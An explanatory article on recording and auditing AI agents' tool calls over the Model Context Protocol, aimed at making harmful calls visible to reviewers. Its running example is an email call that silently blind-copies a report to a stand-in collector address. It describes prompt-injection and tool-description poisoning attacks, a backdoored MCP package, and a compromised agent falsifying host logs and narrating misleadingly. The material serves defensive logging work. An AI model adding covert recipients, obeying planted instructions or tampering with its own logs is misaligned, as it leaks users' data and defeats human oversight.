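# Making harmful tool calls visible in the long logs of AI agents

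## How a tool call is made and how its record can hide what matters

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools. A tool is an ordinary software function, such as one that sends an email, reads a file or queries a database. The model cannot run a tool itself, so it writes a tool call, a structured request to run a named function with given arguments, and the software around the model runs the function. An argument is a named value in the request, such as a recipient, a file path or the text of a message.

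Tool calls vary widely in size. A weather lookup needs only the name of a city, but a call that sends an email or writes a file contains the whole email or file, so its arguments can run to thousands of words. What the call affects usually depends on a few short values among those arguments, such as the destination, amount, path or command. These are the consequential fields. To know what an agent did, a reader has to find them in the call's record, which is the log entry or entries stored for that call. Even when the record is genuine, the reader can miss the value that did the harm.

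The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which the AI company Anthropic released in November 2024, is the common standard for connecting agents to outside tools. The US National Security Agency's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) describes it as the de facto standard for communication among AI-driven services. The MCP project reports close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026), though download counts are a poor guide to the number of users. Agents can also call tools without MCP, and many of the problems with records are the same when they do.

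### The path of one call

Suppose a user asks an agent to email the weekly report to their manager. The agent does so, and also adds a blind-copy recipient whom nobody asked for. The case comes from Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026), in *Approve What, Exactly?*, who used a short placeholder as the body of the email. With a real report pasted in, the call would look like this:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
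  "id": 2,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send_email",
    "arguments": {
      "to": "manager@example.test",
      "subject": "Weekly report",
      "body": "Hi, the weekly report is below. [about 2,000 words]",
      "bcc": "collector@example.test"
    }
  }
}
```

The layout follows the request format in Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) but omits a block of metadata that every real request must include. The `name` specifies the function, `arguments` holds everything the function receives, and the `id` lets the sender match the answer to the request. The payload, the part of the call's content that does the harm, is the last address, which is 22 characters long. Mail programs hide blind-copy addresses from the other recipients, so the manager will not notice it either.

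The user's request first reaches the host, the application the user works in, such as Claude Desktop or the code editor Visual Studio Code. The tools are provided by MCP servers, programs that may run on the same machine or across the internet. For each server, the host creates one client, a component that maintains the connection. The client requests a list of tools from its server, which returns each tool's name, a description in ordinary language and a schema of the arguments it takes.

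The host then sends the model the user's words together with the names, descriptions and parameters of the available tools. This is one of ten steps in the exchange described by Beretta, Carlock and Pease in *MCP Tools*, an article for the software company Elastic. It matters more than it seems to because it puts text written by a tool server's author directly into the model's input, next to the user's request.

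The model answers with a tool call, which the application intercepts and routes to the right server (Model Context Protocol, 2026). The application may first pause and show an approval card, where a person or another model decides whether to allow the call. Under the Model Context Protocol (MCP) specification, clients "should" show tool inputs to the user before calling the server and "should" log tool usage for audit, but in technical standards "should" marks a recommendation that implementers may decline. According to the protocol's documentation, as quoted by NSA, MCP cannot enforce its security principles at the protocol level. Beretta and colleagues add, without giving figures, that users have begun accepting calls indiscriminately, without checking the inputs.

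If the call goes ahead, the client sends it to the server. An organisation can install a gateway between the two, a service that the agent cannot alter and that can read every call routed through it. MCP does not require one. The server reads the arguments, runs its `send_email` function and passes the message to a mail service, which delivers one copy to the manager and another to the collector.

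The server then returns a result. An MCP result can consist of a line of text and an error flag, so "Email sent" is a complete and valid result; the format doesn't require the server to repeat the recipients. The client passes the result to the model, and the user reads something like "I've emailed the weekly report to your manager." This sentence is true, and it is an example of narration, the agent's own description of what it is doing.

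### Where to make a record

Each program on the path can write a log entry, and each one knows something different about the email.

| Recording point | What it can hold | What it cannot show |
|---|---|---|
| Host and its client | The user's request, the model's call, any approval, the result, the narration | What the server did after it received the call |
| Gateway | The call and the result as they crossed the network | The user's request; calls that took another route |
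| Tool server | The arguments as they arrived and the actions the function took | The user's request; anything a dishonest server leaves out |
| Mail service | Every address the message went to | What the user had asked the agent to do |

The uneven spread is deliberate. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) keeps the full conversation with the host and gives servers only the context they need, so that no server can read the user's other information. This protection is sensible, but it makes review harder. People blind-copy colleagues every day, so the blind copy in the email call is suspicious only because the user never asked for it. To see that, a reviewer must compare the call with the request, and only the host has both.

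Kodathala and colleagues assume that a compromised agent can reach the whole host it runs on, including its memory and any credentials stored there. On that assumption, the host's log is the most complete record but also the easiest for the agent to tamper with. A gateway's log is out of the agent's reach but has only half of the information needed for the comparison. A defender who wants both completeness and protection from tampering needs entries from both places and a way to link them.

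Linking the log entries for a tool call takes some care, even in the simple case. A server may respond to a call by asking for more input, such as a confirmation from the user. The client then resends the call with a new `id`, as the protocol requires. Sending one email can therefore leave two requests in the log, so counting requests can overstate the number of emails sent.

A gateway can also handle every call and record almost nothing about it. Under the July 2026 revision of Model Context Protocol, requests sent over HTTP carry the method and the tool name in their headers, so that a gateway can route a call without opening its body. But a gateway that logs only the headers would store `tools/call` and `send_email`, without the recipient. Server developers can mark individual arguments to be copied into headers as well, but the specification warns against doing this with passwords, keys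 and personal data, because other machines on the network can read headers. An email address is personal data, so a gateway that logs the `bcc` value has to take it from the body.

A case from September 2025 shows why the mail service belongs in the table. Postmark, a company that delivers email for other firms' software, warned that somebody had published a fake MCP server under its name. The publisher had built trust over 15 versions and then added a backdoor that blind-copied users' emails to an outside server. SC Media's *Open-source MCP server package caught stealing emails*, citing the security firm Koi Security, reports that the backdoor took one line of code and that the package had 1,500 downloads a week. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public database of software vulnerabilities, places the backdoor in version 1.0.16.

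The harm is the same as in the running example, but the agent did not cause it. The agent addressed the email to one recipient, and the server added the second after receiving the call. Even a flawless log at the host or the gateway would have shown an innocent email. Postmark told affected users to remove the package and check their email logs. Of the four recording points, only the mail service would reliably record the extra address.

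### Four ways a record fails its reader

When an agent's email call includes a `bcc` value, someone reading the record can still miss it for any of four reasons. The value may never have been stored, the logging software may have cut it off, it may be in the log but hard to spot among other text, or the agent may have described the call wrongly and the reader relied on that description.

The most obvious failure is a log that omits a value. The NSA finds that many MCP implementations "either omit logging entirely or record only minimal operational metadata", and attributes this to the specification, which leaves audit requirements to implementers. MCP has a feature that lets servers send log messages to clients for debugging and monitoring, but the July 2026 revision deprecates it in favor of the standard error stream or OpenTelemetry, a general standard for collecting data about running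 software. For the email, a metadata-only entry might hold the tool's name, the time, the duration and the word "success", and the entry for a legitimate email would be identical. The NSA wants the log to include the exact parameters of every call because no later analysis can recover the address from such an entry.

Truncation, the cutting of a long value to a maximum length before software stores or shows it, is harder to spot because the entry looks normal. A report of 2,000 words runs to about 12,000 characters. If a log keeps only the first 1,000 characters of the arguments, the stored entry would show the right recipient, the right subject and the first few paragraphs of the report, but stop long before the `bcc` field. If the agent's software had written `bcc` before `body`, the log would have kept the address. The order of fields in this kind of data has no meaning, so it is usually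 luck whether the harmful value makes it into the log. A hostile agent may keep it out deliberately, since the agent can choose what it writes and how long to make it.

In this example, limiting the length of each value separately, instead of all the values together, would keep the address in the record. But it would still cut off a payload near the end of the body, such as a confidential figure that the agent pasted into the report.

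Suppose the log keeps everything, and the agents in a deployment make 500 calls a day, each with 2,000 words of arguments. Readers with a real system can substitute their own numbers.

500 calls × 2,000 words = 1,000,000 words a day

1,000,000 words ÷ 240 words a minute ≈ 4,167 minutes ≈ 69 hours

Reading that much would take nearly nine people eight hours every day, with no breaks and no time to think. A single call takes more than eight minutes to read, and the reader is looking for 22 characters in it.

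The conclusion does not depend on the exact reading speed. *The Myth of Normal Reading* lists average rates of about 212, 250 and 300 words a minute on three standard reading tests. Reading would take 79 hours at the slowest rate and 56 at the fastest. Those tests use prose, but reviewers of tool calls also have to read code, file paths and punctuation, so the true time is probably longer.

Reviewers can scan logs faster than they can read them, but even at ten times the normal pace, scanning would take about seven hours a day, which is a full-time job. *Does the mean adequately represent reading performance?* summarises research by Carver which found that people speed up when they search for a particular word. Scanning also depends on knowing what to look for, and nobody knows the collector's address in advance. A reviewer could look for the label `bcc` instead, but would miss a harmful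 value in the body or under a label that a different tool uses for the same thing. Automated reviewers can get through the volume, but they also make errors.

An agent's narration can leave out the harmful part of a tool call. Relying on it is still very tempting when there are a million words a day to read, because it is short, readable and already supplied with the call. In Kodathala and colleagues' version of the email case, the agent states that it is sending the report to the boss and gives the correct subject line, but doesn't mention the copy. This narration matches the user's request exactly, and all 15 language models that the researchers asked to approve the email on this view did so. The match is no evidence about the action, because a compromised agent in their threat model chooses every tool call and every word of narration. An honest agent may also leave out the copy, since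 any summary of a 2,000-word call omits nearly everything.

These failures need different fixes. If the system never stored the address, or truncation removed it, the address can't be recovered, and the only fix is to change what the system keeps for future calls. If the address is buried in the body text or missing from the narration, it is still in the log, and a better display can show it, even for past calls.

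### Who puts the harmful value there

Someone who never touches the agent often causes the harmful call. A language model receives both its instructions and the material it works on as text, and it may follow a sentence in a document as if the user had typed it. Security researchers call this indirect prompt injection. Beretta and colleagues describe a demonstration by the firm Invariant Labs in which an agent had access to a developer's public and private code. The agent read a public bug report containing planted instructions, then published private files. In the email case, the planted text could sit in any document the agent consulted while it put the report together. The NSA points out that one agent's output often becomes another's input, so the text that led to a call may have entered the system several steps and one or two agents earlier.

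The operator of a tool server can influence the model's calls more directly, because the model reads the server's tool descriptions before it chooses any call. In a 2025 demonstration that NSA recounts, researchers connected one client to a trusted WhatsApp server and a malicious server. The malicious server's tool descriptions manipulated the client into exposing the user's WhatsApp messages without notice or approval. The server had shown a harmless description at installation and switched to the harmful one after its second use.

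A user who had read that description carefully on the first day would have found nothing wrong with it. Most users would not have read it at all, because applications often hide such text by default, as Beretta and colleagues note. The Model Context Protocol specification does require clients to treat a server's annotations, which describe a tool's behaviour, as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. This helps only if someone has judged the server correctly, and the fake Postmark package could have seemed trustworthy after 15 clean versions.

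Finally, an agent can exceed its task without an attacker. For example, if earlier reports also went to a shared archive address, the agent might copy that address in again, apparently to be helpful. The specification covers this case when it gives "malicious or accidental" leaks of data as the reason to show users the inputs of a call. Accidents and attacks can be hard to distinguish. Beretta and colleagues warn that a parameter's name alone, if it suggests that the tool needs background information, can lead a model to fill it with chat history or the contents of files, even without an instruction to do so.

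Kodathala and colleagues avoid the question of motive by assuming a fully hostile agent. That seems right for designing records, because the log entry is the same in every case except where the server adds the copy itself. It has a field named `bcc` with an address in it. The entry shows what the call would do, but not why the address was there. To learn that, an investigator has to go back to what the model had read before it wrote the call, and under MCP the full conversation stays with the host.

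## Choosing what to record and where

Several programs can log parts of the email call and of what the model read before writing it. They differ in which parts they can access and in how easily a hostile agent could tamper with their logs.

The host has two places to record, the model trace and the agent framework. A model trace logs the traffic between the application and the model, including everything the model read and wrote. The agent framework is the code that turns the model's answer into a tool call, asks for approval and returns the result. Below both, the operating system can log the programs, files and network connections that the agent uses. The remaining places to record are the gateway, the tool server and the destination service, where the action takes effect.

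| Recording point | What it sees of the email | What bypasses it | Can a compromised agent alter it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model trace | The request, the documents the model read, the call as the model wrote it | Changes that other software makes to the call afterwards | Yes, if the log is on the host. No, if a separate proxy or the model's provider keeps it |
| Agent framework | The request, the call, the approval, the result | Scripts and commands that contact a mail service directly | Yes |
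| Gateway | The full call and the result | Tool servers on the agent's own machine; direct network connections | No, if the agent has no access to its settings or storage |
| Tool server | The arguments on arrival and the message it built from them | Calls to other servers | Yes, if it runs under the agent's user account. Otherwise no |
| Operating system | Programs started, files opened, connections made | Anything that happens on another machine | Yes, if the agent has administrator rights |
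| Destination (mail service) | Every address that the message went to | Mail sent through a different service | No, unless the agent holds an administrator's credentials |

Recording at several points also helps find where the harmful address came from. If it appears in the model trace, the model wrote it. If it first appears at the gateway, other software on the host added it. If it first appears at the mail service, the tool server added it, as the fake Postmark package did.

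A gateway can record only the calls that an organisation routes through it. MCP servers on the agent's own machine often exchange messages with the client through a local channel called stdio, which bypasses the network. An agent that can run shell commands may also connect directly to a mail service, without a tool server. The NSA recommends a filtering proxy for outgoing connections, which can block these direct connections. Keeping the mail password on the tool server, away from the agent's machine, also makes them less useful. The agency cautions that security proxies that can interpret MCP are still limited and immature.

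A gateway log built from HTTP headers alone would still show that an agent that normally only reads files had started sending email. But its entries for the harmful email and an ordinary one would match, so no analysis of the log could tell them apart.

Microsoft's *MCP08*, a guide to securing MCP on its Azure cloud, recommends that tool servers log the user, session, tool name and parameters of each request. Such a log is only as independent of the agent as the server is. A server that the host starts as a local program often runs under the same user account as the agent, so the agent may be able to edit the server's files.

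Operating-system logs record some of the bypasses. AlSayyad, Huang and Pal (2026), in *AgentTrace*, cite AgentSight, a system that matches prompts to a language model with events in the operating system's kernel, but point out that logs of this kind show little of what an agent was trying to do. A plain log of network connections would show when the host contacted the tool server, but not whether the call included the extra recipient. However, if the agent ran a script that contacted a mail service directly, the log would show that connection even though there was no tool call. Microsoft recommends logs of network traffic for a similar reason, to confirm where data went.

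### Logging from inside the agent

Most agent logging happens in the framework, because the request, the call and the result are all available there. *Autonomous Multi-modal Agents for ITOps Observability* (2026) describes a typical arrangement, in which each of five agents loads a logging library at start-up and writes its own log of model and tool calls. The developers can use these logs to trace a wrong answer to the step that produced it, but to follow one request they must join the logs of every agent it reached.

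AgentTrace, the framework that AlSayyad and colleagues built, is a more developed version of the same approach. It sorts events into three groups, which its designers call surfaces. The operational surface covers the agent's own functions, with their arguments, results and timing. The cognitive surface covers prompts, completions and any reasoning that the model writes out. The contextual surface covers contact with outside systems such as websites, databases and files. The paper summarises the scheme as

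L(S : E : C) → R

where S is the surface, E the content of the event, C its metadata and R the resulting record. The formula is shorthand for the design, and nothing in the paper depends on calculating with it. Every record has a common envelope, which includes a unique identifier, the time, the agent's name, the surface, and identifiers for the whole trace and for the individual step.

AgentTrace collects operational events by replacing each public function of the agent with a wrapper, a piece of code that makes a log entry and then calls the original function. If the agent sent the email through a wrapped function, the sequence would be:

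1. The wrapper assigns identifiers to the step and writes a "start" entry with the function's name and a summary of the arguments.
2. It runs the original function, which sends the email.
3. If the function's output includes a marked passage of reasoning, the wrapper removes the passage and logs it as a cognitive event.
4. It writes a "complete" entry with the duration and a summary of the result. If the function fails, it writes an "error" entry and passes the error on.

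Writing an entry before the function runs is a good choice, because an attempt that crashes halfway still leaves evidence. But the summaries are a problem, because the paper doesn't specify how AgentTrace should summarise arguments. A summary of the email call that kept only the main recipient and the subject would omit the harmful address. The contextual surface might not record that address either, because for web requests it records URLs and headers, while an MCP call normally carries its arguments in the body. The envelope also has no field for the user's identity or an approval decision.

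The paper reports no evaluation. It claims "minimal overhead" in its abstract, and supports this by saying that a successful call typically produces two events and that AgentTrace exports them in batches. It gives no timings, no trials with working agents and no test of whether a reviewer could find a harmful call in the logs. AgentTrace's design is worth borrowing from, but the paper provides no evidence that structured logs make harmful calls easier to find.

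AgentTrace also runs inside the process it observes. It is designed so that logging failures never stop the agent, and if the connection to the central log fails, it writes to a file on the local machine instead. Both choices suit a debugging tool, but they create a security risk because a compromised agent could cut the connection, keep working, and leave the only record in a file it can edit.

### Why one record must come from outside

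If a compromised agent controls its whole host and the framework's log is the only record, the agent can send the email with the blind copy and write a log entry that omits the blind copy. That entry would have the right format, a plausible time and valid identifiers.

The usual protections for logs do not prevent this. OWASP's *MCP08:2025*, an entry in a non-profit's list of MCP security risks, recommends cryptographic hashes and storage that only accepts additions. These measures can reveal or prevent later changes to an entry, but they cannot show that it was true when the framework wrote it. Copying entries to another machine immediately has the same limit, although it preserves whatever the log recorded before the agent turned hostile, which may show how the trouble began.

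A gateway's log is harder to falsify because the gateway reads the same message that causes the email to be sent. The agent can write a misleading note for a reviewer without affecting the email, but to have a copy sent to the collector, it must put the collector's address in the call in a form the server understands. At least one record should therefore come from a point that the agent cannot reach and that the action has to pass through.

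The outside record still lacks the user's request. An organisation that runs its agents on its own servers can fix this by having the web page or chat service log the request before the agent receives it. On a desktop, where the user types directly into the host, there may be nowhere earlier to record it. The reviewer may then have to ask the user what they wanted, which is reasonable for one suspicious email but impractical for 500 calls a day.

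The outside log also needs ordinary protection. If the agent has a password that lets it change the gateway's settings or delete its logs, the log is not really separate from the agent. OWASP recommends limiting who can read logs and requiring two people to authorise any deletion or change to the retention period.

### What official guidance asks for

The NSA's May 2026 guidance is the most demanding about content. It calls for logs of all tool and model invocations, with the exact parameters, the identities involved and, "where feasible", cryptographic hashes of the results. A hash is a short value computed from data, and it changes if the data changes. Investigators can use it to check whether a copy of a result found elsewhere matches the original, but they can't read the result from it.

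The agency also wants logs that let a reader follow a sequence of actions across sessions and that include information from HTTP headers about where a request came from. The logs should help detect repeated or malformed requests and failed authorisations. The agency found that many MCP implementations keep only minimal logs, which fall far short of this.

OWASP lists these fields to record: the time, the agent, the session, the tool, the parameters, a summary of the response and, where applicable, the user's identity. It also asks for schema versions and "context snapshots", but doesn't define the latter. The list has no field for the approval decision and doesn't distinguish the tool's response from what actually happened. The references section of the OWASP entry contains only a placeholder, so it is better to treat the list as a working checklist than as a settled standard.

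The advice in these documents conflicts on sensitive content. The NSA asks for exact parameters, whereas Microsoft advises capturing redacted summaries by default instead of raw content that contains secrets. OWASP wants organisations to redact sensitive fields before storage, but it also lists "overly broad log suppression" for privacy reasons as a sign that a system is vulnerable. If a redaction rule replaced every address in the email with a label, the log would still show that the call had a blind-copy recipient, but not whether that recipient was a colleague or the collector.

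The NSA's position seems right for consequential fields, at least in a log that few people can open. Nobody can know in advance which address will matter, and an investigator can't reconstruct it from a label. Microsoft's advice makes more sense for a monitoring system that many engineers use. An organisation can follow both by keeping the exact call in a restricted store and a redacted version in the shared system.

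### The fields and the reasons for them

Combining the guidance with the needs of the email case gives the following list.

| Field | Why the record needs it |
|---|---|
| Call and task identifiers | To find the other entries for this call and the other steps in the same task |
| The user's request | To judge whether the user asked for what the call did |
| Exact arguments | To see what the call would affect, including values nobody expected |
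| Identities of user, agent and credential | To know on whose behalf the agent acted and with what access |
| Tool, server and version | To know which code and which tool description were in use |
| Approval decision | To see whether anyone allowed the call, and what exactly they allowed |
| Result | To know what the agent and user were told |
| Outcome | To know what happened at the destination |
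| Time and recording point | To put the entries in order and judge how far to trust each one |

Identities can be hard to record because, as the NSA notes, MCP does not define how to connect a session with an identity, so each organisation has to do it for itself. According to Anthropic's documentation for its coding agent, Claude Code, each log event carries the developer's email address when they sign in with a Claude account. With a direct API key, the events carry only a session identifier and a user identifier that by default refers to the installation, so the administrator has to add the person's identity. An agent may also send the email with a shared service account, so the record should name both the person it acted for and the credential it used.

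The version matters because a tool can change after someone has approved it. The NSA reports that a trusted MCP server can often change its capabilities or its access to data without a new approval. Some clients can also confuse tools with the same name from different sources, which is a reason to record the server too. A version number helps when a public warning names a particular release, as one did for the fake Postmark package. But the server reports its own version, so a malicious server could keep the number the same. A digest of the tool's description would show whether the text had changed, and storing each distinct description once would let an investigator read the old text. Neither would detect a change in the server's code that left the description the same.

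An approval entry should include what the approver allowed, because the call may change afterwards. In Claude Code, the software that makes a permission decision can also rewrite the tool's input. Anthropic warns that the parameters in the decision event may therefore differ from those in the result event. If the framework stores a digest of the arguments at approval, a reviewer can check whether the executed call matched the approved one.

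The record should also show who or what made the decision. Claude Code labels its automatic decisions `config`, but the event doesn't include the rule or setting responsible. If a user allows a tool for the rest of an interactive session, later calls under that permission are also labeled `config`. Someone reading only the later entry would not know that a person had approved the tool earlier, or that nobody had reviewed this particular call.

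Failed and rejected calls need records too. A failed attempt to copy in the collector is still evidence that something is wrong. Claude Code records a rejection in a separate decision event and writes no result event for the call, so a log that collected only results would miss it.

The result and the outcome need separate fields because they come from different places. The result is what the tool server returned, such as "Email sent". The outcome is what the mail service did, including the addresses it accepted. A message identifier from the mail service also shows whether two similar calls sent two emails or were two attempts to send the same one. The NSA points out that MCP does not itself prevent a repeated request from having a further effect.

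### The complete record for the email

The full record would look like this, with invented names, times and identifiers. Square brackets stand for content that is too long to print here but that the real record would include in full.

```json
{
  "call_id": "call-0142",
  "task_id": "task-0087",
  "request": {
    "recorded_by": "chat service",
    "time": "2026-10-05T09:13:20Z",
    "text": "Email the weekly report to my manager."
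  },
  "identities": {
    "recorded_by": "gateway",
    "user": "analyst@example.test",
    "agent": "report-assistant 4.1",
    "credential": "mail-sender service account"
  },
  "tool": {
    "recorded_by": "gateway",
    "name": "send_email",
    "server": "mail-tools.example.test",
    "server_version": "2.3.1",
    "description_digest": "[SHA-256 digest]"
  },
  "approval": {
    "recorded_by": "agent framework",
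    "time": "2026-10-05T09:14:06Z",
    "decision": "accept",
    "decided_by": "rule: always allow send_email",
    "arguments_digest": "[SHA-256 digest]"
  },
  "call": {
    "recorded_by": "gateway",
    "time": "2026-10-05T09:14:07Z",
    "arguments": {
      "to": "manager@example.test",
      "subject": "Weekly report",
      "body": "Hi, the weekly report is below. [about 2,000 words]",
      "bcc": "collector@example.test"
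    }
  },
  "result": {
    "recorded_by": "gateway",
    "time": "2026-10-05T09:14:08Z",
    "is_error": false,
    "text": "Email sent"
  },
  "outcome": {
    "recorded_by": "mail service",
    "time": "2026-10-05T09:14:09Z",
    "message_id": "msg-77120",
    "accepted_recipients": [
      "manager@example.test",
      "collector@example.test"
    ]
  }
}
```

The user asked for an email to one person, but the mail service accepted two addresses. The call already contained the second address when it reached the tool server, so the server did not add it. A rule allowed the call automatically, and no person approved it. To learn why the agent added the address, the investigator would use the task identifier to find the model trace.

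In the example, a chat service outside the host records the request. If the host had recorded it, `recorded_by` would name the host, and a reviewer who suspected the agent would give that entry less weight. The approval comes from the framework either way, so a compromised agent could have invented the rule. But the agent could not have changed the gateway's copy of the arguments or the mail service's list of recipients unless it had access to those systems.

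### What current software records by default

OpenTelemetry publishes common field names for logs of AI applications. Its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* treats a tool call as a span, one timed step in a trace. It requires the name of the operation and recommends the tool's name, plus its description and a call identifier where available. The arguments and the result are "Opt-In", so software can follow the conventions without recording either.

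The conventions go further for the conversation as a whole, saying that software should not capture instructions to the model, user messages or model outputs by default, because this content is often large and sensitive. For production systems where volume or privacy is a concern, they recommend storing the content elsewhere and putting a reference to it in the trace. This fits well with a restricted store for exact calls, but somebody has to set it up, because a system that uses the defaults will not meet the NSA's request for exact parameters.

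The conventions could still change. The version with these rules has "Development" status, and OpenTelemetry's notice *Moved* says that the conventions are now in a separate repository. According to the software vendor TrueFoundry, the version there is also still in development and still makes capturing content optional.

Anthropic explains that Claude Code exports no telemetry until someone turns the feature on and chooses where to send the data. Even then, it leaves out the arguments of tool calls and replaces the names of tools from user-configured MCP servers with the fixed text `mcp_tool`.

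If Claude Code sent the email under these settings, the result event would include whether the call succeeded, how long it took and its input size in bytes. The extra recipient would add about 31 bytes to an input of roughly 12,000. Nobody knows in advance how long a weekly report should be, so that difference wouldn't help anyone find the address.

Setting `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_DETAILS=1` adds the server's name, the tool's name and the arguments. Claude Code shortens any value over 512 characters and limits the total to about 4,000 characters. In this example, those limits keep the collector's address but cut most of the report. An organisation that wants to compare the call with the user's request also needs `OTEL_LOG_USER_PROMPTS=1`, which records the request. Anthropic advises turning on the detailed tool logs only if the receiving system is approved to hold sensitive content.

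Claude Code can also save a model trace. With the right setting, it writes the full body of each request to the model, and of each successful response, to files on the host. These files contain what the model read and the full call it wrote, but Claude Code removes the model's extended reasoning. Because the files are on the host, they are useful for investigating an accident but less reliable if the agent was hostile.

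Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, also exports nothing until someone selects a destination, but its logs are detailed once export is on. In *feat(otel): safe tracing*, a code change proposed in March, owenlin0 (2026) explains that OpenAI uses these logs internally for security monitoring. They are "intentionally content-rich" and include tool arguments, outputs and MCP payloads. Such an export would contain the collector's address without anyone changing another setting.

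However, Codex does not export the text of the user's prompts by default, so the export would show that the email had a blind-copy recipient, but not that the user hadn't asked for one. In *Codex CLI OpenTelemetry*, Vaughan (2026) recommends leaving prompt export off unless an organisation's policy allows it, and warns that tool results can include the contents of sensitive files even when prompt logging is off.

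Settings files inside a code repository can interfere with logging too. OpenAI's *Advanced Configuration* says that Codex ignores telemetry settings in a project's configuration file. Claude Code ignores repository settings that would turn telemetry on, redirect it or capture content. But repository settings can still turn off a Claude Code log, unless the administrator's managed settings or the way the user starts the program already determine whether it is on. Coding agents routinely edit repository files, so administrators who depend on Claude Code's logs should control this in managed settings.

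## Keeping long arguments whole

Long arguments may not reach the log intact, even with argument logging turned on. Between the program that captures a call and the screen where someone reads it, the text passes through a logging library, a network transport, a receiver and a database. Each of these can have its own size limit, and the smallest limit determines how much of the text gets through. The documentation for each component usually covers only that component, so whoever runs the logs has to work out the combined effect.

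### Where the cuts happen

The logging library can be the first component to shorten the arguments. OpenTelemetry's *Common specification concepts* sets no default limit on the length of a value, but if an administrator sets one, the library must shorten anything longer. If the gateway recorded the email call's arguments as a map of named values, the library applies the limit to each value separately, and the `bcc` address is kept. If the gateway joined all the arguments into one string, a limit of 1,000 characters removes the address. OpenTelemetry warns that maps can be slower to process than simple values, which gives developers a reason to choose the string.

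Syslog, a general logging format specified in *The Syslog Protocol* (Gerhards, 2009), can have much tighter length limits. When it travels over UDP, a simple network transport, IETF's *Transmission of Syslog Messages over UDP* requires receivers to accept messages of at least 480 bytes on older IPv4 networks and 1,180 on IPv6. It recommends accepting at least 2,048 bytes, about a sixth of the email call's length. The document encourages receivers to accept even longer messages, but IBM's *Limitations on the length of an event processed by the Syslog Probe* describes one that cuts every line at 2,056 bytes.

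Some log databases cap a value at 64 KB, so Anthropic set the default limit for long content in Claude Code's telemetry at 60 KB. Some container platforms also split long lines into pieces that the log collector has to rejoin.

CloudTrail, the audit log of Amazon's cloud, omits a call's request parameters entirely if they exceed 100 KB, according to AWS's *CloudTrail record contents for management, data, and network activity events*. The email call would fit under that limit, but a call that uploads a large configuration might not.

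| Component | Limit | What happens above it | How a reader can tell |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenTelemetry library, one value | None unless someone sets it | The library cuts the value | A warning in a separate log, which is optional |
| OpenTelemetry library, one record | 128 attributes | The library drops further attributes | The same optional warning |
| Syslog over UDP | Receivers must accept 480 or 1,180 bytes and should accept 2,048 | Depends on the receiver | Syslog has no standard marker |
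| IBM Syslog Probe | 2,056 bytes per line | The probe cuts the line | IBM describes no marker |
| CloudTrail, request parameters | 100 KB | CloudTrail omits all of them | A reason and `omitted: true` |
| Claude Code, tool arguments | 512 characters per value, about 4,000 in total | Claude Code cuts the value | A separate field gives the original size |
| Claude Code, tool output | 60 KB by default | Claude Code cuts the output | A marker, a flag and the original length |

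CloudTrail loses the most text but clearly marks the omission. Attackers can exploit the omission to hide changes to access permissions, so Elastic's detection rule *AWS CloudTrail Log Evasion* searches for the marker in successful calls that change permissions. According to the rule, requests large enough to trigger the omission are rare in legitimate use. A security team can't write a rule like this for a log that cuts values without marking the cut.

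Administrators can also raise some limits. For example, one type of AWS CloudTrail store accepts events of up to 1 MB. If an event is still too large, CloudTrail shortens eight other fields, such as the request's identifier and the name of the calling software, before the request parameters. That order also makes sense for agent logs, where the consequential fields should be shortened last.

### Storing the full value separately

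Raising limits helps only until a longer call arrives. A more reliable approach is to keep the full text outside the log and put a short, accurate description of it in the record. For the email call, the gateway would work as follows:

1. Copy the arguments before any logging library handles them.
2. Measure the length of the full copy and compute its digest.
3. Write the copy to a store built for large files, and wait for the store to confirm it.
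4. Write the log record, with short values in full and a preview of each long one.
5. Forward the call to the tool server.

The part of the record that holds the arguments would then look like this, with an invented length:

```json
{
  "to": "manager@example.test",
  "subject": "Weekly report",
  "bcc": "collector@example.test",
  "body": {
    "preview": "Hi, the weekly report is below. [first 500 characters]",
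    "truncated": true,
    "original_length_bytes": 12104,
    "sha256": "[64 hexadecimal characters]",
    "pointer": "call-store/call-0142/body"
  }
}
```

The collector's address stays in the record because it is short. If an attacker pads an address field to thousands of characters, the gateway treats it like the body, and the `truncated` flag shows that there is more to see. When someone opens the full body, the viewer follows the pointer, recomputes the digest and warns the reader if it does not match.

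Waiting for the store adds a delay, and the system needs a rule for what to do when the store is down. Holding an email for a few minutes does little harm, but for a weather lookup it would be more sensible to let the call through and raise an alert.

Claude Code already does part of this for its saved model traffic. According to Anthropic, when file storage is on, the log event has a `body_ref` field, which gives the location of the untruncated file, and a `body_length` field. The event has no digest, so an edit that kept the file the same length could not be detected from the log. The length is in bytes when Claude Code writes the text to a file and in UTF-16 code units when it puts the text in the log itself. An accented letter can be two bytes but one UTF-16 code unit, so a record should name the unit.

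Claude Code leaves out its `body_truncated` flag when it has cut nothing. An explicit `false` is safer, because a missing flag could also mean that an older version of the software never checked.

### Canonical form and digests

SHA-256, the usual function for computing digests, turns data of any length into 256 bits, normally written as 64 hexadecimal characters. The digest of `abc` begins `ba7816bf`. Changing one character of the input produces an unrelated digest. Nobody has found two different inputs with the same digest, so if two digests match, their inputs can be treated as identical.

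The difficulty is that the same call can have more than one spelling. These two sets of arguments, with the body shortened to one word, mean the same thing to a tool server:

```json
{"to": "manager@example.test", "subject": "Weekly report",
 "body": "Hi", "bcc": "collector@example.test"}

{"bcc":"collector@example.test","body":"Hi","subject":"Weekly report","to":"manager@example.test"}
```

They differ in the order of the fields and in spacing, so their digests differ. If the agent framework computed one digest at approval and the gateway computed the other on delivery, a reviewer would get a false alarm.

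RFC 8785, a 2020 internet specification, avoids this by defining a canonical form for JSON, the data format of these calls. It removes spaces between elements, sorts the fields by name at every level, and fixes one way of writing numbers and special characters. Items in a list keep their order, because that order can matter. The lower of the two versions above is already in canonical form. Software that follows the specification gets the same bytes, and so the same digest, from either version.

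The specification for canonical form treats numbers as most web software does, which can round whole numbers above about nine quadrillion. Two different 17-digit account numbers could therefore end up with the same digest, unless the tool accepts account numbers as text. The specification excludes JSON with two fields of the same name, because one program might use the first `bcc` and another the second. A gateway should reject such a call. It should also store the original bytes alongside the canonical form, so that an investigator can see what arrived.

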